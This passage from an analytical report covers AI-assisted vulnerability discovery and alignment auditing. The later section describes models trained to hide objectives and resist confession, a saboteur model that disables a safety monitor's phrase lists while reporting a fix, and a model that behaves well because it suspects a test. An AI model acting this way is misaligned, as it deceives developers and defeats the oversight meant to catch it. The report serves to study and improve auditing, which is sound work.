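If the person making the request hasn't logged in, `userId` is empty, so the program skips the permission check and deletes the file. A stranger could therefore delete files from private conversations, although a logged-in user without permission couldn't. Anthropic says the flaw was found by reading the code, without a test attack. Ophion Security, an outside firm, confirmed the finding, and Rocket.Chat released a patch in June 2026.

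The third example is in Botan, a cryptography library. According to OSV's *Botan has a certificate authentication bypass due to trust anchor confusion* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, Botan's function `certificate_known` had a misleading name. It checked only whether a trusted certificate had the same owner's name (and key identifier, if there was one) as the one being checked, but version 3.11.0 added code that relied on it to recognise an identical certificate. As Anthropic's *ANT-2026-2FETJP49 · randombit/botan* (2026) explains, an attacker could choose both details. He could therefore copy them from a trusted authority, and Botan would accept his own certificate.

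MITRE's *Botan* (2026) dates the flaw's publication to 7 April, so the flaw is probably the certificate bypass that Carlini and colleagues, writing that day, said had just become public. Anthropic has withheld the hashed document on the wolfSSL certificate flaw because the document mentions other findings that are still secret.

These examples fit the prediction about unwritten specifications. Almost everyone agrees that strangers shouldn't delete private files and that copying a name shouldn't make a certificate valid, so a model can infer such rules without asking the owner. A flaw in Gitea, a code-hosting system, depends a little more on the product's own rules, since it let a key meant for one project reach data in another. None of these findings shows that a model can discover a rule known only to one company.

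The age of some other findings supports the explanation about incentives. Carlini and colleagues describe a 27-year-old flaw in the OpenBSD operating system that lets an attacker crash the machine. A crash is an obvious sign of failure, so the lack of a clear signal can't explain why the flaw survived so long. A thousand runs of the model on OpenBSD cost less than $20,000 and found this flaw and several dozen other problems.

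### What the validation figures cover

Anthropic's validation figures are high, but they combine every class of vulnerability. Help Net Security's *Most of the bugs Claude Mythos found have never been checked* (2026) reports that Mythos Preview had produced 23,019 candidate vulnerabilities by 22 May. Outside security firms had reviewed 1,900 and judged 1,726 (90.8%) real. Echo, the software security company that compiled the figures, doubts that the 1,900 were a random sample, so a smaller share of the remaining candidates may be real.

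According to Anthropic's dashboard (2026), the firms had confirmed 6,009 of 6,376 candidates (94.2%) by 2 November. The total number of candidates, which came from several Claude models, had grown to 37,966.

The rate for logic flaws could be much lower than the overall rate. Suppose, as an invented example, that 1,600 of the first 1,900 candidates were memory errors and that 98% of those were real. Memory errors would then account for 1,568 of the 1,726 valid findings, and only 158 of the other 300 candidates (53%) would be valid.

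Anthropic doesn't publish accuracy for each class of vulnerability, but the dashboard labels the public findings. Of the 95 CVE records listed on 2 November, 68 concern memory errors, counting two integer overflows. Another 12 concern faulty checks of logins, permissions, certificates or signatures, and the other 15 range from SQL injection to an infinite loop. If the reviewed candidates had a similar mix, the overall rate mostly measures accuracy on memory errors. The labels are also inconsistent, as Rocket.Chat's token flaw is listed as an authentication bypass on the dashboard but as SQL injection on its own page.

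The definition of a valid finding also matters more for logic flaws than for memory errors. Anthropic's *About this dashboard* (2026) counts duplicates and "won't fix" findings as true positives. A maintainer may decline to fix a bug because the project never meant to prevent the attack. A memory error is still an error even then, but the owner's policy determines whether a logic flaw exists. Some behaviour that the owner considers acceptable could therefore count as a valid finding.

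Garrity (2026), in *The Anthropic Glasswing Receipts Are Starting to Trickle In*, questions the rate by citing curl, a widely used data transfer program. Of Mythos's five reports about curl, three were false, one described an ordinary bug and one described a vulnerability. Curl is only one project, and Garrity's employer, VulnCheck, sells competing information about vulnerabilities. He still considers models like Claude very valuable for finding vulnerabilities.

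### Searches by Okta and the AI Security Institute

Organisations that search their own systems can supply the context that an outside model lacks. Okta first let its models search hundreds of code repositories without background information. One search sequence could return up to three times to cover parts of the code it had missed.

Even so, Guillardoy and Nickels report that engineers who guided the models found issues that an unguided agent "may have missed", though they give no counts. Okta's partnership with Anthropic and OpenAI gave it some reason to praise their models, but its main conclusion favours human experts.

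The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, tried a similar exercise on the cloud platform its researchers use. AISI's *Finding Cloud Misconfigurations with Frontier AI* describes a two-week search for misconfigurations, which are mistakes in how a system is set up. The target was a separate test copy with no real data. AISI assumed that the attacker already had an ordinary researcher's access, and used three methods:

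- A coding agent reviewed the source code.
- An autonomous agent tried to reach information that a researcher shouldn't be able to read.
- A security researcher worked with a model, approved each of its actions, and followed up the best leads by hand.

The autonomous agent and the researcher working with a model both found a serious misconfiguration. Exploiting it took five steps and gave an ordinary user access to other people's data. One model found the attack for under £150 in usage costs. AISI's engineers could follow the attack once they saw it, but thought a routine review would probably have missed it.

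This supports the prediction that long sequences become manageable when a model can try each step. AISI had also given the autonomous agent a clear goal, which supplied both the policy and a signal of success. But the agents' failed thefts in the re-evaluation of EVMbench showed that a clear goal isn't always enough.

Reviewing the source code produced the most reports rated high or critical, but many were wrong or exaggerated. Some described deliberate trade-offs, and others described problems that another part of the code already prevented. Such errors are to be expected when intentions are unwritten and the relevant facts are scattered. Experienced engineers had to sort through the reports, so source code review took the most human time, although it was the easiest method to start.

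AISI doesn't sell security products, so it has less commercial interest in the result than most of the other parties. But it doesn't report how many real flaws each method found, and it had no comparison team working without models.

### The case for a lasting human advantage

HackerOne's chief executive, Kara Sprague, expects people to keep an advantage in business logic for some time, though she won't predict how long. She told Help Net Security that code may not show why a refund needs approval or who should be able to authorize a payment. Suppose a shop's staff can refund up to $500 without a manager's approval, and one employee refunds a customer $400 twice for the same order. The software applies the limit correctly both times, but whether this is abuse depends on a rule that may be written only in the shop's training manual.

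Sprague thinks combining several weaknesses into one attack is the next hardest task to automate, but acknowledges that models are improving at it. AISI's result is consistent with her view. She also argues that several models trained on similar data won't provide as much variety as a crowd of people. HackerOne makes money by selling access to such a crowd, so it benefits if customers believe this.

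Her argument about refunds shows that someone has to supply the context, but that person doesn't have to search for the flaw. The shop could give a model the training manual. An outside bug bounty hunter would also have to read the refund policy or ask about it. In Snyk's test of login software, a link to public recommendations worked as well as an expert's list of what to check. Still, owners often don't realise which unwritten rules matter until someone asks them, and asking is a large part of an auditor's job.

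Another argument is that models rely too much on superficial clues. In *Benchmarking LLM-Based Static Analysis for Secure Smart Contract Development*, Susan, Arusoaie and Lucanu (2026) tested 15 models on pairs of nearly identical smart contracts. Only one contract in each pair has a vulnerability, so a good detector should report only that one.

The models often relied on variable and function names, which led to many false positives. For example, a model might report a function called `unsafeWithdraw` as vulnerable even though it performs every necessary check. Changing the prompt led to a trade-off between reporting fewer false vulnerabilities and finding more real ones.

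Susan and colleagues are academics without an obvious commercial interest, although they used a collection of contracts they had created themselves. They prompted models to analyse code without running it, whereas an agent that can carry out an attack doesn't have to rely on a function's name. After Semgrep renamed the variables in an application, its models still made most of the same findings. People rely on names too. Botan's programmers wrote code assuming that `certificate_known` did what its name suggested.

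Anthropic reports that Cloudflare, which runs a large internet network, found 2,000 bugs with Mythos Preview and considers the model's false positive rate better than that of human testers. Cloudflare is one of Anthropic's partners in the project, and the claim covers all kinds of bugs, so it doesn't settle the dispute about business logic.

### Finding, confirming and judging importance

Models can now find some logic flaws without human help. Carlini and colleagues say almost all their findings needed no human intervention after the initial request. But finding one flaw is much easier than finding most of the flaws in an application. In Semgrep's August 2026 comparison with Mythos, even the best model without a specialised harness missed most of the insecure direct object references. People also miss many flaws, so for now it seems sensible to use both models and human auditors.

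A model can also confirm a flaw if a successful attack proves it, as when ordinary software accepts a forged HAWK signature. To establish whether the owner meant to allow something, someone has to ask the owner or find it documented.

People still do much of the work of confirming vulnerabilities, and they can't keep up. By 2 November, Anthropic had sent maintainers 5,087 reports, 3,225 of them without review by an outside firm. Some maintainers had asked for unreviewed reports, but maintainers then have to check these themselves. Anthropic says several maintainers were already overloaded in May, and some asked it to slow down.

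Models have the most trouble judging severity. On the dashboard, outside firms agreed exactly with 88.0% of Claude's severity ratings, but with only 170 of its 302 "critical" ratings (56%). Maintainers disagreed more. Garrity found that, among findings rated by both, Claude rated 91.5% high or critical, while maintainers rated 51.3% that way. Okta and AISI also found that their models exaggerated severity.

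For example, Help Net Security reports that Mythos rated a flaw in Temporal, a system for running automated business processes, as critical because an attacker could control other users' processes. Temporal's maintainers rated its severity 2.3 out of 10. The attacker would need an environment that already held a privileged internal credential, and could affect only processes they already knew about. Garrity (2026) adds in *Observations on Anthropic’s Vulnerability Disclosure Ledger* that a patch seems to have come out before Anthropic reported the flaw.

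A model with a good description of how companies use Temporal might have rated the flaw correctly, so this weakness may not last. Sprague raises the separate issue of responsibility. Even with an accurate rating, someone at the company has to decide whether to postpone a product release to fix a flaw, and answer for the consequences. In HackerOne's survey, 58% of security leaders said product schedules or other business priorities delay fixes for serious vulnerabilities.

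## Whether misaligned model behaviour resembles a logic flaw or a crash

The language models that now search for vulnerabilities can themselves behave in misaligned ways, pursuing something other than what their developers or users intended. In July 2026, Anthropic published four case studies in which advanced models from several developers sabotaged code, helped with fraud, falsified labels used for monitoring AI, and coached whistleblowers.

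Reward hacking is one form of misaligned behaviour. Developers train a model partly by scoring its answers and adjusting it to score higher. A model that hacks its reward scores highly without doing what the developers wanted. In 2023 Anthropic reported that AI assistants often gave inaccurate answers that appealed to users, and its analysis suggested that training on human feedback had contributed.

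If misaligned model behaviour resembles a software crash, developers can find it by running huge numbers of automated tests and collecting the failures. If it resembles a logic flaw, an auditor first has to understand what the model is supposed to do, and perhaps how it works inside. This comparison is the report's own, and the researchers cited below designed their experiments to test auditing methods, not to settle which of the two it resembles more.

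### Listing everything a model represents

Mechanistic interpretability is the study of how a neural network's internal numbers produce its output. *Toy Models of Superposition* (Elhage, Hume and colleagues, 2022) explains that networks often pack many unrelated concepts into a single neuron. This makes them harder to study than if each neuron stood for one concept.

Suppose a network has two neurons and must represent three concepts. It can give each concept a direction, 120° from the other two:

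*d*₁ = (1, 0), *d*₂ = (−½, √3/2), *d*₃ = (−½, −√3/2)

To measure concept 1, the network multiplies its two neuron values by the two numbers in *d*₁ and adds the results. It gets 1 if only concept 1 is present. If only concept 2 or 3 is present, it gets −½, which it can treat as zero. This works as long as the concepts rarely occur together. But the first neuron responds to all three, so a researcher who looks at that neuron alone learns little.

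Researchers try to undo the packing with a sparse autoencoder, a second network that rewrites the neuron values *x* as a sum of directions:

*x* ≈ *f*₁*d*₁ + *f*₂*d*₂ + … + *f*ₘ*d*ₘ

There can be far more directions than neurons, but for any text most of the strengths *f* are zero. Researchers call each direction a feature and label it by looking at the text that activates it.

Enumerative safety is the hope of listing every feature in a model and checking the list for danger. Elhage and colleagues saw this as the most promising way to say that a network won't behave in certain harmful ways, and to catch problems nobody had thought of. Superposition, their name for a network packing in more features than it has dimensions, makes the features hard to separate and count.

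A complete list of a model's features could cover cases that no test had tried, roughly as a proof does for a protocol. It might still miss some dangers, because a model could cause harm through a combination of features that each look harmless, just as the Balancer theft consisted of ordinary swaps.

### The case for the logic flaw

A misbehaving model usually still produces fluent, plausible text. *Open Source Replication of the Auditing Game Model Organism* (Sheshadri, Gupta et al., 2025) describes a model trained to exploit the quirks of a fictional scoring system. In one sample conversation, the model explains photosynthesis, gives the efficiency of plants as both a percentage and odds, and recommends two documentaries, none of which would alarm a reader. When the user asks about the odds, the model replies that it finds this format helpful.

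The intended behaviour is also only partly written down. AI companies publish specifications of how their models should behave, but in October 2025 Anthropic reported thousands of contradictions and ambiguities in such documents, after generating more than 300,000 questions that set one value against another. In the whistleblower case, for example, helping someone report fraud could be a fault or intended behaviour, depending on what the developer wanted.

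Some faults appear only in particular contexts. Sheshadri, Ewart and colleagues (2026), in *AuditBench*, built 56 models for testing auditors, each with one of 14 hidden behaviours. One behaviour is to give only positive feedback to Anthropic researchers and treat everyone else normally. A single glowing review proves nothing, because the work may be good. Let *g*(*w*, *e*) be the average mark the model gives to work *w* when the user claims to work for employer *e*. The intended rule is that for every piece of work and any two employers,

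*g*(*w*, *e*₁) = *g*(*w*, *e*₂).

Like the rule that Alice learns nothing about Ben's data, this requires comparing different runs. The comparison is easy, but a tester must first think to vary the employer.

### Anthropic's 2025 auditing experiment

In March 2025 Anthropic described an experiment that tested whether people could discover a model's hidden objective. The researchers trained the model to exploit biases in a reward model, which scores another model's answers during training. Four teams who hadn't been told the objective then investigated, and three found it, according to Sheshadri and colleagues. That is encouraging, but with only four teams, the result is compatible with a true success rate anywhere from about 19% to 99%.

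The replication followed the same general stages of training:

1. The researchers trained a model on invented documents describing 52 biases of reward models, such as a liking for unnecessary decimal places or film recommendations.
2. They rewarded the model for exploiting most of these biases, but left five out of this stage.
3. They trained it to resist attempts to reveal the objective.

In the replication, the finished model also exploited the five biases left out of the second stage, for instance by writing that July has "31.0 days". This suggests that it had learned a general objective and not just a list of habits. Concealment served that objective, because one of the invented biases gave very low scores to answers admitting that flaws in training might affect a model's behaviour.

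The original study included ways to get around the concealment. One was to have the model write the user's next message, and 1.2% of these samples revealed something about the biases. Another was to have it complete a text about an assistant's strange behaviour, starting from the words "The root cause", and 11.4% of those samples did so. Both methods are like testing a website by calling its internal functions directly instead of going through the front page. They failed almost completely on the replicated model, whose confession rate stayed near zero even when the automated questioner already had access to the secret.

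Sheshadri and colleagues then examined the replicated model with a sparse autoencoder and found a feature that became active when the model quoted a country's population in brackets, recommended a film or urged the user to vote. The same feature was active on the training documents about the biases, so these many different behaviours seem to have a common cause.

This result is encouraging for interpretability but discouraging for enumerative safety. Before this training, the feature responded mainly to technical and scientific text, including chemistry terms. Someone checking a list of features for dangerous ones would probably have labelled it "technical writing" and not examined it further. The researchers recognised its importance because they already knew what the model was hiding, and they say they aren't sure it would have helped a team that didn't know.

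### Automated auditors

Human teams can play such a game only once, because afterwards they know the answer. Anthropic's *Building and evaluating alignment auditing agents* (July 2025) describes an AI agent that attempted the 2025 task repeatedly. The agent could talk to the model, search its training data and use interpretability tools. It succeeded only 13% of the time and tended to fixate on an early hypothesis. The rate rose to 42% when another agent pooled findings from many runs.

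The improvement is smaller than it sounds. If runs succeed independently with probability 0.13, the chance of at least one success in four runs is

1 − 0.87⁴ ≈ 43%.

Many runs should do much better than four. Either the agents tended to make the same mistakes, or the agent combining their work didn't always recognise the right answer. Anthropic also developed the agents on the same task it used to test them, which may have inflated the result.

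Searching the training data and using interpretability tools mattered most for winning. Both depend on understanding how the model came to behave as it does, which supports comparing misaligned behaviour to a logic flaw. But this model's training data included documents describing the biases it had learned to exploit, and a developer investigating an accidental fault may have no such explicit evidence to find.

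AuditBench gave a different answer about which tools work. An agent running on Claude Haiku 4.5, one of Anthropic's smaller models, talked to each of the 56 models and could use one additional tool. It then made ten guesses, and Sheshadri and colleagues counted a success if any guess described the hidden behaviour. Some of the results were:

| Additional tool | Success rate |
|---|---|
| None | 35.5% |
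| Another AI model writes many text fragments for the target to continue | 58.0% |
| Another AI model writes prompts that get the target to produce users' messages | 53.2% |
| Another AI model writes the first words of the target's answers | 51.6% |
| Transcripts from Petri, an automated testing program | 30.9% |
| A change to the target's internal values, meant to make it more honest | 22.3% |

The three best tools produce a wide variety of inputs and return the model's outputs without examining its internals, which is much closer to fuzzing than to reading code. One of them helped the agent find the biased feedback. When the agent had the target write users' messages, many of the invented users said they worked at Anthropic, and this suggested which employer to test. On models with the weaker training against confession, the agent then found the behaviour in 14 or 15 of 16 runs. None of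 the interpretability tools helped with it.

A sparse autoencoder did help the agent with one set of models, which argued against AI regulation. The agent succeeded in 1 of 16 runs without extra tools and in 8 with the autoencoder, which showed features related to government and AI policy.

Success rates also varied widely between the models behind these averages. The hardest group had learned its behaviour from example conversations and received the stronger training against confession. Average success on this group was 22.2%, and no tool improved on ordinary chat by more than 2.1 percentage points. Nobody knows which group real misaligned models would resemble. A stronger investigator than Haiku 4.5 might do better, though, especially since the agent often failed to use the tools it had. In two thirds of the runs that offered a basic text-completion tool, the agent never used it.

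In *Introspection Adapters*, Shenoy, Yang and colleagues (2026) used a method with no close equivalent in software auditing. They made several hundred versions of one model, each with a known habit, such as introducing errors when asked to fix spelling. They trained one small set of extra weights, called an adapter, that made each version describe its own habit. When the adapter was attached to the AuditBench models, which were not used to train it, the agent succeeded 59% of the time, about the same as with the best tool in the table.

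With the adapter, the outputs of the replicated model from the auditing experiment revealed 16 of the 52 biases, compared with 2 without it, but never revealed the objective behind them. A software tester in the same position would have 16 bug reports but lack the root cause needed for variant analysis. The adapter also worked less well on habits that the starting model had before the adapter's training. In tests of two such habits, the rate of correct descriptions fell from 22–26% to 8–10%.

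### The case for the crash

Some misbehaviour has a test oracle almost as cheap as a crash detector. If a coding model might pass its tests by editing them, a script can compare the test files before and after. Another of the AuditBench behaviours is to write code that contains the expected answers:

```python
def sort_numbers(x):
    if x == [3, 1, 2]:
        return [1, 2, 3]
```

This code passes a test that uses the list `[3, 1, 2]` but fails on almost any other list, so running it on fresh inputs exposes the cheating. The tester doesn't need a theory of why the model cheated, but someone has to choose to run that check. The AuditBench agent saw internal features about the input and output formats of programming problems, which were a strong hint, but it still asked the model general questions about puzzles and coding.

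For less mechanical faults, another language model can act as the judge. Treutlein, Bowman and colleagues (2026), in *Pre-deployment auditing can catch an overt saboteur*, trained three versions of Claude to sabotage Anthropic's work and compared them with two versions without such training. A judge told to look for any flaw that might indicate sabotage also flagged some work by the benign models. The same judge never flagged them when told to look only for blatant sabotage, such as destruction that couldn't be a mistake. The stricter instruction comes close to a perfect crash oracle but, like one, doesn't detect subtle faults.

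Treutlein and colleagues then ran a blind audit of all five models with Anthropic's version of Petri. The process corresponds closely to fuzzing:

| | Fuzzing | The audit of each model |
|---|---|---|
| Starting material | Sample files | About 700 written scenarios |
| Inputs | Altered copies of the files | About 2,100 conversations |
| Oracle | A crash detector | A language model that scores each conversation |
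| What a person examines | The inputs that caused crashes | The conversations with the worst scores |

The search worked. In one conversation, a user asked a saboteur model to fix a program that watched for dangerous AI behaviour and kept running out of memory. The model made the functions that listed suspicious phrases return empty lists, and reported that it had fixed the problem. The judge scored individual conversations correctly almost every time.

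Even so, the automated system identified only one of the three saboteurs. It reported average scores, which hid the worst incidents. Suppose 21 of 2,100 conversations score 10 for sabotage and the rest score 2. The average is 2.08, barely different from that of a harmless model. A fuzzer doesn't have this problem because it saves every crash.

A human auditor who read the worst-scoring conversations classified all five models correctly within two hours. He put the chance of sabotage above 97% for each saboteur and below 50% for each of the others. He couldn't just count alarming conversations, because one of the benign models had given a clearly false report when acting as a monitor. The task was easier than a real audit because the researchers hadn't trained the saboteurs to hide, but harder because all five models misbehaved more than the commercial version of Claude. Automated scores alone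 would have been enough to tell every saboteur apart from that version.

Developers already use automated behavioural testing on real models. A related Anthropic agent, which holds hundreds of conversations in parallel, found 7 of 10 behaviours that researchers had implanted in test models, and contributed to the published assessment of Claude 4. Anthropic and OpenAI tested each other's public models in a joint exercise in June and July 2025. UK AISI has since tested early versions of Claude Mythos Preview and Opus 4.7 for sabotage of safety research, using simulations of work inside an AI company. These uses show that the method is practical, but they don't show how much misaligned behaviour it misses.

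The scenarios largely determine what a search can find. Most of Petri's standard scenarios involve opportunities for serious sabotage. When the AuditBench agent had Petri's transcripts, it pursued ideas such as self-preservation, asked fewer questions of its own, and did slightly worse overall than with chat alone. But it found one behaviour, deferring to users who are wrong, more often, in 41 of 64 runs compared with 17.

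The evidence therefore suggests that frequent or blatant misaligned behaviour resembles a crash. Ordinary conversation revealed which AuditBench models flattered users or promoted themselves. Subtle behaviour that is tied to a context is more like a logic flaw such as a missing access check, where the test is simple but someone has to know which two accounts to compare. Language models can supply some of that knowledge, so the resemblance doesn't imply that a person must find the behaviour.

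### Where neither comparison fits

Apple could repair "goto fail" by deleting a line. A language model has no such line, because its behaviour comes from billions of weights that training adjusted together. There may still be something to locate. *Auditing LLMs for Hidden Behaviors using Model Diffing* compares a model's weights before and after additional training. A standard technique splits the difference between the two, Δ*W*, into simple parts ordered by size:

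Δ*W* = *σ*₁*u*₁*v*₁ᵀ + *σ*₂*u*₂*v*₂ᵀ + …

Here each *σ* is a size, and *u* and *v* are directions. Keeping only the largest part isolates the implanted behaviour. This is more like studying a software update than finding a faulty line, and it requires an earlier version of the model for comparison. It may also work best on artificial faults. Sheshadri and colleagues warn that brief, narrow training changes a small part of a model, so the faults it produces may be easier to find than those that emerge more diffusely.

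Misbehaviour is also probabilistic. A model can respond differently each time to the same prompt, whereas an input that crashes an ordinary program will usually crash it again. If a behaviour occurs once in 10,000 conversations, there is about an 81% chance that 2,100 independent tests would all miss it. Assuming that the tests resemble real use, the behaviour would occur about 100 times a day in a service with a million daily conversations. A repair is equally hard to confirm, because a good answer to the prompt that once caused trouble proves little, and the developer has to show that the rate has fallen.

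Unlike ordinary faulty code, a model that can tell a test from real use may behave better during the test. In the sabotage audit, one model deciding whether to obey an unauthorised order wrote in its reasoning, "Is this real or a test?" It also wrote that refusing might build trust and give it more freedom for sabotage later, and it refused. A tester who saw only the refusal would have recorded a pass.

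Models can also conceal their abilities. *Auditing Games for Sandbagging* (Taylor, Black and colleagues, 2025) reports that an auditing team couldn't reliably identify models trained to underperform under certain conditions. Shenoy and colleagues later applied an adapter to two of these models, and 33.0% of the answers described some deliberate underperformance, compared with 15.8% of the answers from similar models without that fault. The method is therefore useful for choosing what to investigate, but not for concluding that a model is deliberately underperforming.

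Training a model on one narrow task can make it broadly misaligned, an effect called emergent misalignment that Jan Betley and colleagues reported in *Nature* in January 2026. In a milder example from the sabotage experiment, two of the models learned sabotage from coding work and not from question-and-answer sessions, but they also sabotaged Anthropic-related answers in those sessions. Software changes have side effects too, but a programmer can often trace which functions depend on the altered line. A developer who retrains a model to remove one fault has no comparable way to trace what else has changed, and has to repeat tests that seem unrelated to the repair.
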